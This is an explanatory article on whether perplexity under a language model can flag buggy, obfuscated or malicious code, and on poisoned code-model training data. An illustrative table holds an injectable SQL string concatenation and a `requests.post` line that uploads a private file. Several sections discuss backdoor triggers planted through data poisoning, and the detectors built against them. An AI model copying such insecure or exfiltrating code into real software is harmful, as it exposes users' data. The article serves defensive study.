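# Perplexity as a Test for Malicious Code: What Statistical Typicality Can and Cannot Show

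## What perplexity measures and how it is used as a security check

Perplexity measures how well a language model predicts a text. A language model assigns a probability to every possible next piece of a text, based on the pieces before it. The higher the probabilities it gave to the pieces that did come next, the lower the perplexity. A speech recognition group at IBM first used the term in this sense. According to the textbook chapter *N-gram Language Models* (Jurafsky and Martin, 2026), perplexity is still the standard way to measure a language model apart from any application.

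Programs are also text, so anyone with a suitable model can compute the perplexity of source code. Researchers have done so to look for bugs, disguised malware and training examples that an attacker has tampered with. In each case, they assume that harmful code looks unusual, so a model of ordinary code will predict it badly.

### From tokens to a score

A language model works with units called tokens. In code, a token may be a keyword, a variable name, an operator or a bracket, though large language models often split a long name into several tokens. *On the Naturalness of Software* (Hindle, Barr and colleagues, 2012) gives the example of a programmer who has typed `for(i=0;i<10`. The obvious continuation is `;i++){`, and a decent model of code gives those tokens a high probability.

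The surprise of a token is the negative logarithm of the probability that the model gave it. A token with probability 1 has a surprise of zero, and the surprise grows as the probability shrinks. Averaging the surprise over all n tokens of a text gives the cross-entropy, and the exponential of that average is the perplexity:

surprise(xᵢ) = −log p(xᵢ | x₁ … xᵢ₋₁)

perplexity = exp( [surprise(x₁) + … + surprise(xₙ)] / n )

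Some papers take logarithms to base 2, report the cross-entropy in bits and raise 2 to that power. The perplexity comes out the same. Suppose a model reads four tokens and gives them these probabilities:

| Token | Probability | Surprise (natural log) |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 0.9 | 0.11 |
| 2 | 0.8 | 0.22 |
| 3 | 0.5 | 0.69 |
| 4 | 0.01 | 4.61 |

The surprises add up to 5.63, the average is 1.41, and the perplexity is about 4.1. A model choosing among roughly four equally likely tokens at every step would get the same value. The first three tokens alone have a perplexity of about 1.4. The fourth token supplies more than four fifths of the total surprise, and it clearly raises the perplexity only because the text is so short.

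Perplexity also depends on both the text and the scoring model, which is the model that supplies the probabilities. Jurafsky and Martin trained three simple models on the same 38 million words from the *Wall Street Journal* and scored one test text with each. The perplexities were 962, 170 and 109. "Low perplexity" therefore means low under a particular scoring model. Two models' perplexities are comparable only if the models share the same vocabulary of tokens.

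### Why code is so predictable

The three *Wall Street Journal* models were n-gram models, the simplest kind of language model. An n-gram model predicts a token from only the n−1 tokens before it, using counts from its training data. To find the probability that `;` follows `i < 10`, a 4-gram model divides the number of times all four tokens appeared in a row by the number of times the first three did. A sequence that never occurred in training would get probability zero and therefore infinite surprise, so in practice a correction called smoothing reserves a little probability for unseen sequences.

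Hindle and colleagues used such models to find out whether software is as repetitive as ordinary language. They took ten Java projects and two collections of English text, trained on 90 percent of the lines, tested on the remaining 10 percent, and repeated this over ten random splits. English fell from about 10 bits per token with a model that used no context to just under 8 bits with a 10-gram model. Java was far lower, in some cases below 2 bits. In perplexity terms, 8 bits is 256 and 2 bits is 4. Most of the improvement came by the 3-gram or 4-gram model, so two or three preceding tokens capture much of the regularity in a program. *Do People Prefer "Natural" code?* (2019) puts the gap between Java and English at 3 to 4 bits, which makes code 8 to 16 times more predictable.

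Much of Java's regularity seems to come from habit, not just from having a stricter grammar than English. If grammar were the whole explanation, a model of one Java project should predict other Java projects about as well as its own. Hindle and colleagues tested this by training 3-gram models on ten projects, and every project had a lower cross-entropy under its own model than under the other nine. *Studying the Difference Between Natural and Programming Language Corpora* (2018) found that Java was still more repetitive than English after corrections for grammar and syntax, and that legal and technical English were repetitive in a similar way.

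Researchers call this property naturalness, the degree to which code resembles the code a model was trained on, as measured by low average surprise. It depends on the training code, so a program can be natural by one standard and odd by another. The word can also mislead by suggesting that the code is wholesome. The later journal version of *On the Naturalness of Software* compared C programs from ten application areas, such as mail, graphics and networking. Cross-entropy was 3 to 4.5 bits within an area, while the medians across areas were 5 to 5.5 bits. *What is the Difference Between Me and You?* (2026) still uses this method, training one n-gram model per author, human or AI, and measuring how well each predicts the others' code.

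### Three ways to turn the score into a check

The simplest check computes one perplexity for the whole item and raises an alarm if it exceeds a fixed threshold. *Beyond Heavy Log Curation* (2026) does this for log entries, which are a computer system's records of its own activity. A model trained on normal logs scores each new entry given the earlier ones, and any entry above the threshold counts as an attack. The paper acknowledges its key assumption that attacks leave entries with a different vocabulary, syntax and sequence from normal ones. An attack that leaves ordinary-looking entries would therefore pass the check.

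The same rule can apply to source files, but a sensible threshold is harder to find. *The Fools are Certain; the Wise are Doubtful* (Kotti, Dritsa and colleagues, 2025) scored 2,254 files from 881 GitHub projects and found that, across models, perplexity was high for Shell scripts and low for Java. A single threshold for both languages could therefore flag a harmless Shell script just because it is written in Shell.

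A whole-file score may also miss a short malicious passage, because the passage has little effect on the average. *CodeSentinel* (2026) gives this as its reason for scoring smaller units of code. One remedy is to compare the lines of a file with one another. *Beyond Natural Language Perplexity* (Tsai, Yu and colleagues, 2025) does this with DEPA, a detector for dead code (valid code that does nothing useful) that an attacker has inserted into training examples. For a file of ten lines, DEPA makes ten copies, each missing a different line, and computes the perplexity of each copy together with a description of the task. The score of line 4, for example, is the average over the nine copies that contain it. DEPA flags each line whose score is more than 1.5 standard deviations above the mean for the file.

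Because each line is compared with the rest of its own file, a program written in an odd style throughout does not stand out. But almost every file has a least predictable line, and if line scores followed a normal distribution, about 7 percent of the lines in a clean file would exceed the DEPA threshold.

The deletion score asks how much the perplexity of a text falls when one token or line is taken out:

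deletion score of token i = perplexity of the whole text − perplexity without token i

In the four-token example, the last token has a deletion score of about 4.1 − 1.4 = 2.7. Deleting an earlier token would also require the model to rescore the tokens after it, because their context changes. The score can be negative. Deleting a closing bracket, for instance, usually makes the rest of a program harder to predict. DEPA's line scores are deletion scores in another form, since a line ranks high exactly when the copy without it has a low perplexity.

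Deletion scores for code come from ONION, a defense for ordinary text, and are used mainly against data poisoning. An attacker plants altered examples in a training set so that the trained model misbehaves, typically whenever its input contains a certain token or code fragment, called the trigger. A trigger that does not fit its surroundings should have a high deletion score, but ordinary tokens can too. *Show Me Your Code! Kill Code Poisoning* (Sun, Chen and colleagues, 2025) scores a code snippet token by token, and the common C tokens `static` and `uint8_t` both score above zero, ONION's threshold for flagging a word.

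### Unusual, faulty, insecure and malicious

All of these checks measure how unusual a piece of code is. Their users want to know something else, and it is easy to slide from one property to another. Four short examples keep them apart:

| Property | Example | What makes it so |
|---|---|---|
| Unusual | `int R = 3 + V1++;` | It packs an addition and an increment into one statement; `int R = 3 + V1; V1++;` does the same in two |
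| Faulty | `if (total > 50) shipping = 0;` | The shop promised free shipping from 50 upward, and an order of exactly 50 still pays |
| Insecure | `"SELECT * FROM users WHERE name = '" + name + "'"` | A visitor can type database commands where the program expects a name |
| Malicious | `requests.post(url, data=open(path).read())` | Inside a calculator app, it sends a private file to a stranger |

The unusual line is harmless. It comes from a 2025 paper by Abdelsalam, Peitek and colleagues. *How do Humans and LLMs Process Confusing Code?* examines "atoms of confusion", short snippets that are valid and correct but that programmers tend to misread. The researchers used the language model Qwen2.5-Coder-32B to measure the perplexity of confusing and clean versions of the same code. Perplexity consistently spiked at the confusing constructs, and the spikes correlated with brain responses that earlier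 researchers had recorded from programmers reading the code. The high perplexity reflected how hard the code was to read, not an error or an attack. Such snippets are common in large, respected projects, including the Linux kernel.

The other three lines look ordinary. Whether the shipping rule is faulty depends on what the shop promised, which may not appear in the program. The database query is insecure because of what an outsider can do with it, whatever its author intended. Code is malicious if someone wrote or altered it to do harm that its user has not agreed to, so malice depends on purpose and consent. An identical `requests.post` line would be legitimate in a backup program that the user installed to copy files to a server.

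A program can have several of these properties at once. Malware that its author has scrambled to resist analysis is both malicious and unusual, and a careless bug may also open a security hole. Perplexity directly measures only the first property, unusualness. It can indicate the other three only where they occur together with unusualness, and experiments are needed to find out how often they do.

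### Measuring a detector

Experiments of this kind report a few standard measures. For example, a detector might check 1,000 files, 100 of which are harmful, and flag 180 files, of which 90 are harmful and 90 are harmless.

- **Recall** is the share of harmful items that the detector flags, here 90 of 100, or 90 percent.
- **The false positive rate** is the share of harmless items that it flags, here 90 of 900, or 10 percent.
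- **Precision** is the share of flagged items that are harmful, here 90 of 180, or 50 percent. It depends on how common harmful items are. With fewer of them in the pile, precision would drop even though the detector had not changed.

Lowering the threshold catches more harmful files but also flags more harmless ones, so a recall figure means little without the false positive rate. The area under the curve (AUC, or AUROC in some papers) does not depend on a choice of threshold. It is the chance that a randomly chosen harmful item gets a more suspicious score than a randomly chosen harmless one. A value of 0.5 is no better than guessing, and 1 is a perfect ranking. Results are awkward to compare across papers because they report different measures. Sun and colleagues report recall and the false positive rate, while Tsai and colleagues report AUC and the F1-score, which combines precision and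 recall.

These measures mostly describe flagged code, but trust concerns the code that isn't flagged. In the example, the detector leaves 820 files unflagged, and 10 of them (1.2 percent) are harmful, compared with 10 percent of all the files. This lower rate justifies more trust in unflagged files only if future harmful files are as easy to detect as the ones in the test.

Using a high score as a reason to look more closely is fairly uncontroversial. Ray, Hellendoorn and colleagues (2015), in *On the "Naturalness" of Buggy Code*, called improbable code "possibly suspicious" and expected from the start that some correct lines would look unnatural and some buggy lines natural. The appeal of using a low score as a reason to look less closely is that it saves work. Kotti and colleagues mention that reviewers could check a language model's code suggestions less closely when the model had high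 confidence in them. Their concern is correctness, and nobody is trying to hide an honest mistake. The author of malicious code may be trying to hide it, which raises the question of whether a low score justifies any trust at all.

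## The inference from low perplexity to harmless code

Anyone who treats a low score as reassurance is reasoning from the text of a program to its effects. Written out, the argument has four premises:

1. Harmful code is rare in the data from which the scoring model learned.
2. The model finds rare code surprising.
3. The final score keeps that surprise visible.
4. The attacker cannot remove the surprise, or does not try.

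If all four premises hold, harmful code gets a high perplexity, so code with a low perplexity is harmless. The conclusion follows, but the score has to be much more reliable for clearing code than for raising an alarm. An alarm that catches only a fifth of harmful programs is still useful if it seldom goes off for harmless ones. Someone who used the same score to clear code would let the other four fifths through. To clear code safely, the premises have to hold for nearly every harmful program. If each held for 90 percent of harmful programs, independently of the others, only about 66 percent of those programs would get a high score.

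### What each premise needs

The first premise is plausible if it refers to harmful purposes, since few programmers set out to steal files. But a language model learns from text, so the text of the code must also be rare for the inference to work. The calculator app's upload line isn't rare in this sense, since legitimate backup programs can use the same line, and some insecure snippets are common.

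Rarity alone does not make code surprising. Almost every program of any length is unique, but a model can predict one it has never seen if the steps are familiar, such as reading a file or sending data to a server. For the second premise to hold, the model has to assign these steps a lower probability because they are out of place in, say, a calculator app. A large model might do so if the earlier code makes the app's purpose clear, but a 4-gram model has too little context.

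The third premise depends on how much a few tokens can change a file's average. Suppose the tokens of a 1,000-token file have an average surprise of 1 nat, and an attacker replaces ten of them with tokens that have a surprise of 5 nats. The total rises by 40 and the average by 0.04, so the perplexity goes up by about 4 percent. A whole-file score can reveal the change only if the scores of ordinary files differ by less than that. Line scores and deletion scores avoid the averaging, but they can reveal the malicious line only if it stands out among ordinary lines.

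The fourth premise matters only when the harm is deliberate. It holds only if the attacker cannot estimate the score, or if any rewrite with a lower score would stop the attack from working. An attacker who can write the same attack in many ways can pick the most ordinary one.

### The best test compares two sources

Statistics offers a more exact way to say when perplexity should work. Let p(x) be the probability that ordinary programming produces program x, and q(x) the probability that an attacker produces it. Flagging x adds p(x) to the false positive rate and q(x) to the recall. Someone with a limited budget of false positives should therefore first flag the programs that add the most recall per false positive, and continue until the budget runs out. That means ranking programs by the likelihood ratio:

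likelihood ratio(x) = q(x) / p(x)

The Neyman–Pearson lemma, a theorem from 1933, states that no other test has a higher recall at the same false positive rate. As *Evaluating Epistemic Uncertainty* (2026) points out, the ratio therefore also gives the best possible AUC. *Falsehoods that ML researchers believe about OOD detection* (2022) derives a version for individual items. If a share α of all programs is harmful, then

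P(harmful | x) = 1 / (1 + (1 − α) / (α · likelihood ratio(x)))

Apart from the ratio, the text of the program has no bearing on the answer.

Perplexity is an estimate based on p alone. Among programs of equal length, ranking by p matches ranking by q/p only if q is flat, meaning that the attacker is equally likely to produce any text. Zhang, Xiao and colleagues (2024), in *Your Finetuned Large Language Model is Already a Powerful Out-of-distribution Detector*, compare this assumption to a monkey at a typewriter. *FLatS* (2023), a paper on detecting unfamiliar text, also warns against it and argues that a detector needs both a low p and a high q. The assumption doesn't hold for attackers, because their programs have to run and do something specific, and so share most of their structure with ordinary code.

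At the other extreme, harmful code is just ordinary code that happens to do harm. Let p now describe all code in circulation, including the harmful part, and suppose that attackers produce each harmful program in proportion to its p. A world with only four programs is enough to show the result:

| Program | Does harm? | p | q | q/p |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| A | No | 0.4 | 0 | 0 |
| B | Yes | 0.4 | 0.8 | 2 |
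| C | No | 0.1 | 0 | 0 |
| D | Yes | 0.1 | 0.2 | 2 |

The ratio is 2 for both harmful programs, although B is four times as probable as D. Attackers and everyone else both write a predictable program (p = 0.4) 80 percent of the time, so a detector that uses only p has an AUC of 0.5. A detector based on what the programs do makes no mistakes.

A detector that uses only the perplexity score can do no better than use the ratio P(harmful | score) / P(harmful). Perplexity is therefore informative exactly to the extent that harmful code is more common at some scores than at others. Whether this is true of real code is an empirical question.

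Low perplexity cannot guarantee in general that code is harmless. Zhang, Goldstein and Ranganath (2021) proved in *Understanding Failures in Out-of-Distribution Detection with Deep Generative Models* that no test does better than chance against every possible alternative source, even if it uses the true distribution p. One of their constructions takes several items that are equally probable under p and shifts all of their probability onto a few of them. The new source then produces exactly the same distribution of scores as the old one. An attacker can do the same by using only the harmful programs at each level of predictability.

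### When a score is too low

A very low perplexity can itself be abnormal. Suppose a coin lands heads 90 percent of the time, and a model assigns heads a probability of 0.9 on each toss. The most probable run of 100 tosses is 100 heads, which has a perplexity of 1/0.9, or about 1.11. Yet that run occurs only about once in 38,000 attempts.

A more typical run has about 90 heads and 10 tails, and its perplexity is about 1.38. Each run with exactly ten tails is 3.5 billion times less probable than all heads, but there are 17 trillion such runs, and together they account for 13 percent of all attempts.

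Information theorists call runs like these typical. A source's typical set contains the sequences whose average surprise is close to the source's entropy, which is its long-run average surprise. For long sequences, this set holds nearly all of the probability, even though it may exclude the single most probable sequence. A check that flags only high perplexity would rate 100 heads as the most normal result possible, although such a run suggests a two-headed coin. A code file that repeats one line a thousand times would also have low perplexity, because a model soon predicts every repetition, but few people write such files.

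### Foreign images with better scores

Low scores for foreign data became a well-known problem in work on images. Researchers there were studying out-of-distribution detection, the task of recognising inputs that come from a different source than the training data. Nalisnick, Matsukawa and colleagues (2018), in *Do Deep Generative Models Know What They Don't Know?*, trained an image model called Glow on CIFAR-10, a collection of small pictures of animals and vehicles. They then scored new pictures from CIFAR-10 and pictures of house numbers from another collection, SVHN. The house numbers should have surprised the model more, but they surprised it less:

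| Training images | Familiar test images | Foreign test images |
|---|---|---|
| Animals and vehicles | 3.46 bits | House numbers: 2.39 bits |
| Clothing | 2.96 bits | Handwritten digits: 1.83 bits |

The figures are the average surprise per pixel value, in bits. The same thing happened with PixelCNN, which predicts an image one pixel at a time, much as a language model predicts text. But a Glow model trained on house numbers did not give the animals and vehicles a better score than the house numbers.

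Caterini and Loaiza-Ganem (2021), in *Entropic Issues in Likelihood-Based OOD Detection*, explain this asymmetry with a standard identity. If a model P scores data from a source Q, then

average surprise = D(Q‖P) + H(Q)

The first term, the Kullback–Leibler divergence, measures how far the source is from the model and is zero only if they match. The second is the entropy of the source, or how unpredictable it is. Data from another source adds divergence, but its entropy may be lower by more than that amount. For example, under the model of the 90 percent coin, a two-headed coin has a divergence of 0.105 and an entropy of 0, while the 90 percent coin itself has a divergence of 0 and an entropy of 0.325. The two-headed coin therefore gets the better score, even though the model matches the 90 percent coin perfectly.

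An experiment by Kim and Yoon (2026), in *Mitigating the Likelihood Paradox in Flow-based OOD Detection*, supports this explanation. They added random noise to the house numbers and left the model unchanged. Likelihood was poor at picking out the foreign images when there was hardly any noise, but the AUC rose close to 1 with slightly more. The pictures still showed house numbers but had become harder to predict.

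Zhang, Goldstein and Ranganath attribute the problem to the models instead. In their view, a correct model of animals and vehicles would give house numbers zero probability, and existing models get this wrong by a tiny amount. To show how small an error is enough, they consider a million equally probable legitimate items and 10,000 foreign ones that should be impossible. If a model moves 1 percent of the probability to the foreign items, each of them becomes slightly more probable than each legitimate item, yet the average surprise of legitimate data rises only from 13.816 to 13.826. A model can therefore do very well in ordinary tests while making this error.

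Le Lan and Dinh (2020) argue in *Perfect Density Models Cannot Guarantee Anomaly Detection* that better models would not be enough. Image models of this kind usually work with densities, meaning probability per unit of volume. Re-encoding the same images in different coordinates stretches some regions and shrinks others, which changes the densities. Le Lan and Dinh proved that a suitable re-encoding can produce practically any ranking of the images by density without losing information. A density therefore cannot identify an anomaly without some further assumption about what anomalies look like.

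The two sides also disagree about whether familiar and foreign images come from separate ranges. Zhang, Goldstein and Ranganath find this reasonable, while Le Lan and Dinh are sceptical, since even slight random noise makes every image possible under both sources. Overlap is much harder to dispute for code, because honest and malicious programs can share the same upload function. Even a perfect model of ordinary code has to give that function a fair probability. Fixing the model's errors would not remove this overlap, and every test makes some mistakes when the sources overlap.

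### Repairs and their limits for code

*A Probabilistic Circuit-Induced Pseudo-Metric for Out-of-Distribution Detection* (2026) still calls the problem the "likelihood paradox" and lists repairs based on likelihood ratios, model ensembles, complexity corrections, typicality and other statistics. These repairs differ in how well they transfer from pixels to tokens.

Likelihood ratios transfer most directly to code. Ren, Liu and colleagues (2019), in *Likelihood Ratios for Out-of-Distribution Detection*, tested one on DNA, which is a sequence of discrete symbols, like a tokenised program. They trained a model on known classes of bacteria and used it to look for sequences from classes discovered later. Plain likelihood had an AUC of only 0.626, mainly because it depended heavily on the proportion of the letters G and C in a sequence, a background property that varies widely among bacteria.

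To correct for this, Ren and colleagues trained a second model on copies of the data with some letters randomly changed. This model still learned the general letter frequencies but lost most of the meaningful patterns. Dividing the first model's probability by the second's cancelled much of the background and raised the AUC to 0.755. For images of clothing and handwritten digits, the AUC rose from 0.089 to 0.994. In a source file, brackets, keywords and boilerplate could be the background, and could produce a low perplexity regardless of what the few important lines do.

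Zhang, Xiao and colleagues obtained even larger gains with ordinary text. They fine-tuned a language model on newsgroup posts and used the original, general-purpose model as a stand-in for q. When they looked for movie-review sentences among the posts, the AUC was 0.008 with likelihood alone and 1.000 with the ratio. The 0.008 overstates the problem for perplexity, because they used the probability of the whole text, which tends to be higher for short texts. With longer movie reviews, the AUC was 0.755 with likelihood alone and again 1.000 with the ratio.

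But these ratios detect text from an unfamiliar source, which may be harmless. To detect malicious code, q would have to describe malicious code. A security team could estimate q by training a model on known malware, but the estimate would be accurate only for attacks that resemble the known ones.

Another repair, based on typicality, flags scores that are too low as well as too high. In *Detecting Out-of-Distribution Inputs to Deep Generative Models Using Typicality*, Nalisnick, Matsukawa and colleagues (2019) compared the average surprise of a batch of images with the average for the training data. They set the threshold by repeatedly drawing batches from held-out familiar images. With Glow trained on images of animals and vehicles, the test flagged 42 percent of two-image batches of house numbers and every ten-image batch, at a false positive rate of about 1 percent. It failed when familiar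 and foreign images had nearly the same distribution of scores. With PixelCNN trained on images of clothing, for example, it flagged only 1 percent of batches of letters, even with 25 images per batch.

A code reviewer usually has to judge one file at a time, so the results for large batches are of limited use. The test would also do no better than chance in the four-program world, because it uses the same score as perplexity and only measures distance from the average. Zhang, Goldstein and Ranganath raise a more basic objection, which also applies to the 90 percent coin. If the run of 100 heads replaces one run with ten tails in the typical set, the set stays the same size and its total probability rises. Size and probability alone therefore give no reason to call 100 heads abnormal. One also needs an idea of what might have gone wrong, such as a two-headed coin, and that amounts to choosing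 a q.

Geometric fixes for likelihood tests are harder to apply to tokens. In *A Geometric Explanation of the Likelihood OOD Detection Paradox*, Kamkari, Ross and colleagues (2024) argue that images unlike the training data can lie in regions where density is high but volume is so small that the total probability is close to zero. This explains why a model never generates such images despite their high likelihood. They accept an image as familiar only if it has a high likelihood and can vary in enough independent directions under the model. Token sequences have probabilities instead of densities, and there is no smooth space around a program in which to count directions.

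Le Lan and Dinh acknowledge that their proof does not directly apply to discrete data. They describe a looser equivalent, in which someone has to decide which inputs count as the same. The choice of tokens is one such decision. For code, the more important one is whether to count two programs with different text but identical behaviour as one program or, as language models do, as two.

### Same behaviour, different score

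Changing a variable's name from `total` to `qz7` throughout a function leaves its behaviour the same, but the new name will probably be harder for a model of ordinary code to predict. *Do People Prefer "Natural" code?* tested this on Java by shuffling the variable names within each method. Average surprisal rose, and it rose about twice as much when names moved between variables of different types, such as a number and a piece of text.

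Renaming is the most common behaviour-preserving change in research. *Semantic-Preserving Transformations as Mutation Operators* (2025) found 94 kinds of such change in 28 publications, 25 of which renamed variables. These changes do not always make code look odd. In *Towards Reliable Evaluation of Neural Program Repair with Natural Robustness Testing* (2024), human judges considered 58.8 percent of the changed programs natural and 19.3 percent unnatural. One of the unnatural programs differed from the original only in renaming the variable `v` to `V`. *Uncovering the Limits of Machine Learning for Automatic Vulnerability Detection* (2023) applied eleven kinds of change, which on average did not make the code less natural as measured by cross-entropy. The effect of renaming on perplexity depends on the new names, and whoever writes the code chooses them.

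A tiny edit can also change what a program does while hardly affecting its perplexity. The loop `for (i = 0; i < n; i++)` goes through the n elements of a list. If `<=` replaces `<`, the loop runs one extra time, and in C it may then overwrite memory that belongs to something else. Both operators are common in loops, so a model might give `<` a probability of 0.6 and `<=` a probability of 0.3. The edit would then add 0.69 to the total surprise. In a function of 200 tokens, this would raise the perplexity by about 0.35 percent if the later tokens kept their probabilities.

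Now suppose someone renames a variable that occurs ten times in the same function, and the surprisal of each occurrence rises by 1. The perplexity rises by about 5 percent. This harmless edit changes the perplexity roughly fifteen times as much as the edit that can corrupt memory.

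## Where unusual code is also faulty or disguised

Bugs and obfuscation provide the best evidence that unusual code deserves suspicion. Some bugs, such as a `<=` in place of a `<`, are inconspicuous, but many break a pattern that the rest of the program follows, so a model that has learned the pattern assigns the broken line a low probability. Obfuscated code, which someone has rewritten to be hard to read without changing what it does, often departs even further from ordinary code.

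### Buggy lines before and after repair

Ray and colleagues looked for this effect in ten Java projects, including the database Derby and the search library Lucene. They selected 8,296 commits (recorded changes to the code) whose messages contained a word such as "bug", "error" or "fix". They labeled the lines deleted in these commits as buggy and the lines added as fixed. The labels are rough, because a repair can also delete correct lines, but they provided 88,058 lines labeled buggy to compare with 58 million unchanged ones.

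The scoring model combined two n-gram models. One learned from other files in the project, and the other, called a cache, learned only from the file under examination:

p(token) = γ/(γ + c) · p_project(token) + c/(γ + c) · p_file(token)

Here γ is a constant, and c is the number of times the preceding tokens occur elsewhere in the file. As c grows, the file's own patterns get more weight. Each line's score was the average surprise of its tokens, in bits.

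When a fix deleted only one or two lines of a file, the buggy lines scored 1.67 to 1.80 bits higher than other lines, and their replacements scored about 1.5 to 1.6 bits lower than the buggy lines. When Ray and colleagues included every fix of up to 30 deleted lines, the two differences shrank to about 0.8 and 0.55 bits. They suspect that large fixes delete many ordinary lines that are only indirectly related to the error.

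Even the larger gap between buggy and other lines, 0.56 standard deviations, leaves a lot of overlap. If both groups had normally distributed scores with the same spread, the AUC would be about 0.65, or 0.57 with the larger fixes included.

In the networking project Netty, a programmer called `setSuccess` where the code needed `trySuccess`. The faulty line averaged 5.96 bits per token and the corrected one 1.34, because the same file already used `trySuccess` three times. The method depends on having such a pattern for comparison. A harmless new logging statement scored high because the project contained nothing like it. A copied line with the wrong variable name scored low because it repeated code the model had already processed.

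### Using surprise to search for bugs

Ray and colleagues measured how many bugs a reviewer would find by starting with the most surprising lines of code and working down. For a reviewer with time to read only 5 percent of the lines, ranking by plain surprise did only 17 percent better than a random order. For a reviewer who could read 20 percent, it did nearly twice as well as random.

Many lines are surprising for harmless reasons. A class declaration introduces new names that the model cannot predict, whereas the first line of a `for` loop usually follows a fixed form. Ray and colleagues therefore compared each line only with lines of the same grammatical type:

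adjusted score = (surprise of the line − mean for its type) / standard deviation for its type

They then gave more weight to the types that had most often contained bugs. With both changes, the ranking did more than twice as well as a random one over the first 5 percent of lines. Part of this gain came from the project's bug records rather than the language model.

The adjusted score performed about as well as PMD and FindBugs, two widely used programs that check code for known error patterns. The comparison covered bugs discovered after release in five Apache Software Foundation projects. Surprise was most useful for sorting these tools' warnings within each priority level, which worked significantly better than using the tools alone.

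A later comparison was much less favourable to ranking lines by surprise. In *Predicting Defective Lines Using a Model-Agnostic Technique*, Wattanakriengkrai, Thongtanunam and colleagues (2020) ranked the lines in 32 releases of nine Java systems. Their own method, Line-DP, predicts which files are defective and then marks the lines containing the tokens that most influenced the prediction. In the top 20 percent of lines, Line-DP found 91 percent more defective lines than ranking by surprise, but only 53 percent more than a random order. Ranking by surprise therefore found about 20 percent fewer defective lines than the random order.

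Wattanakriengkrai and colleagues also tried a fixed threshold for surprise. The differences they report imply that it flagged roughly 42 percent of defective lines and 45 percent of clean ones, which is no better than guessing.

The test may have put the surprise ranking at a disadvantage. The random order covered only files that a separate model had already marked as likely to be defective, and the paper doesn't mention this filtering in its description of the surprise ranking. The surprise ranking also lacked the adjustment for line types, so declarations full of new names probably rose to the top. But PMD found only about 5 percent more defective lines than the random order, so matching PMD is a modest achievement.

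### What larger models added

The bug studies described so far used n-gram models. *Exploring the Naturalness of Buggy Code with Recurrent Neural Networks* (Lanchantin and Gao, 2018) repeated the experiment on one of the ten projects with a neural network that can carry information over much longer stretches of code. Buggy lines averaged 1.65 and other lines 1.59, and the AUC was only slightly higher than with the n-gram model.

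Karampatsis, Babii and colleagues (2020), in *Big Code != Big Vocabulary*, found a clearer benefit. They used 357 bugs from Defects4J, a collection of real Java bugs and their repairs, and measured how much each repair lowered the snippet's average surprise. The drop was 1.81 percent under an n-gram model and 5.98 percent under their largest neural model. The snippets included some unchanged lines around the bug, which makes both percentages smaller. In the text, they mention drops of 70 percent and more, but those figures match the improvement over the n-gram model, not the drop in surprise.

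This test compares each bug with its repair, which a reviewer looking for an unknown bug does not have. *Revisiting Unnaturalness for Automated Program Repair* (Yang, Kolak and colleagues, 2024) came closer to the reviewer's task. It used three code models with roughly 7 to 15 billion parameters, along with the results of the program's tests. A tool first runs the tests and gives a high suspicion score to lines that run mainly in the failing ones. The method then takes the six or ten most suspicious lines, hides each in turn, and uses a model to score how surprising the line is, given the code before and after it. Finally, it sorts the lines by surprise.

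Adding surprise to a test-based tool's ranking raised the number of Defects4J bugs with a faulty line in the top five from 94 to 145, out of 395. One reason is that the tool often gives several lines the same score, and surprise can break the tie. In one bug from a charting program, a missing check could cause a crash. The faulty line ranked tenth using the tests alone and second after sorting by surprise.

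Yang and colleagues also used surprise to choose between possible repairs, scoring each by how much it lowered the surprise of the line:

gain = surprise of the old line − surprise of the new line

Trying repairs in this order meant testing an average of 24 fewer repairs per bug. Ranking by gain also put a correct repair first 49 percent more often than Shibboleth, a specialised ranking tool, did. For the charting bug, the correct repair had a gain of 0.25, while a wrong repair that passed all the tests had a gain of −1.18. The order was only partly right, because a repair that failed the tests had a gain of −0.39 and so ranked above the wrong repair that passed.

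Memorization may explain some of these results. The repairs in Defects4J are public, and a model that has memorized the repaired file would assign the buggy version a low probability for that reason alone. When Yang and colleagues asked GPT-4 to fix the charting bug, it also named the original commit. InCoder, which supplied the scores in this example, failed to fix the bug when asked directly, so memorization is a less likely explanation for its scores.

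Surprise helped at every stage, but Yang and colleagues call the idea that predictable code is correct "specious". A model may rank a subtly wrong solution in several readable lines above a correct but difficult one-line solution, because each token of the wrong one is easier to predict. Judging correctness also requires information from outside the code, such as test results and the developer's intentions.

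Some recent work prompts the model to locate the bug instead of using its probabilities. *Large Language Models for Fault Localization* (2025) tested four models this way. All of them did much worse on Defects4J than on HumanEval-Java, a collection of small programming problems, and all improved when the prompt included the bug report, which can describe what the program should have done.

Scoring small pieces of code is better supported than scoring whole files. *Can Perplexity Serve as a Cognitive Signal for Code Understandability?* (2026) reaches a similar conclusion about code that people find hard to understand, which may be free of bugs. It advises against using a single perplexity score for a whole snippet and describes surprise at particular places as more promising.

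### Early tests for packed programs

Malware authors often disguise their programs to get past antivirus software and slow down analysts. One method, called packing, compresses or encrypts most of the program and adds a short routine that restores it when it runs. Li, Yu and Yin (2025), in *ALMOND*, describe earlier attempts to detect such disguises. Lyda and colleagues used entropy, which in this setting requires no language model. The standard calculation finds the share f(b) of a file's bytes that have each of the 256 possible values b:

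byte entropy = −Σ f(b) · log₂ f(b)

In encrypted data, all byte values occur about equally often, so the byte entropy is close to the maximum of 8 bits. Ordinary machine code has lower entropy because some byte values occur far more often than others.

Byte entropy ignores the order of the bytes, but a language model's predictions depend on it. A file that counts from 0 to 255 over and over has a byte entropy of exactly 8 bits, yet a language model would soon predict every byte. An obfuscator can also rearrange a program's instructions without much changing how often each byte value occurs.

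In 2015, Kanzaki and colleagues used a method closer to perplexity. They trained an n-gram model on normal code and used it to measure "code artificiality", assuming that obfuscation disrupts the usual sequences. According to Li and colleagues, statistical tests like these often work well only against particular kinds of obfuscation.

### How ALMOND scores a program

ALMOND, the detector that Li and colleagues built, applies the same idea with a small GPT model. It works in four steps:

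1. A disassembler translates the program's machine code into assembly language, which spells out each processor instruction, such as `MOV RBP, RSP`.
2. ALMOND splits the instructions into tokens and replaces numbers, strings and addresses with placeholders. These values vary so much that they would surprise the model even in ordinary programs.
3. The model predicts each token from the ones before it. It has 87 million parameters and learned only from ordinary code, taken from 5,200 Linux and 3,000 Windows programs.
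4. ALMOND combines the probabilities into a score and flags code whose score exceeds a threshold.

The model itself never trained on obfuscated code, but Li and colleagues did use labelled obfuscated examples to choose the threshold.

They first considered plain perplexity as the score. But the model guessed more than 70 percent of the tokens correctly even in obfuscated code, and these easy tokens looked much the same everywhere, with an average perplexity of 1.28 in obfuscated code and 1.12 in ordinary code. Error-perplexity leaves them out. It uses only the set M of tokens for which the model's first guess was wrong:

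error-perplexity = exp( [sum of surprise over all tokens in M] / |M| )

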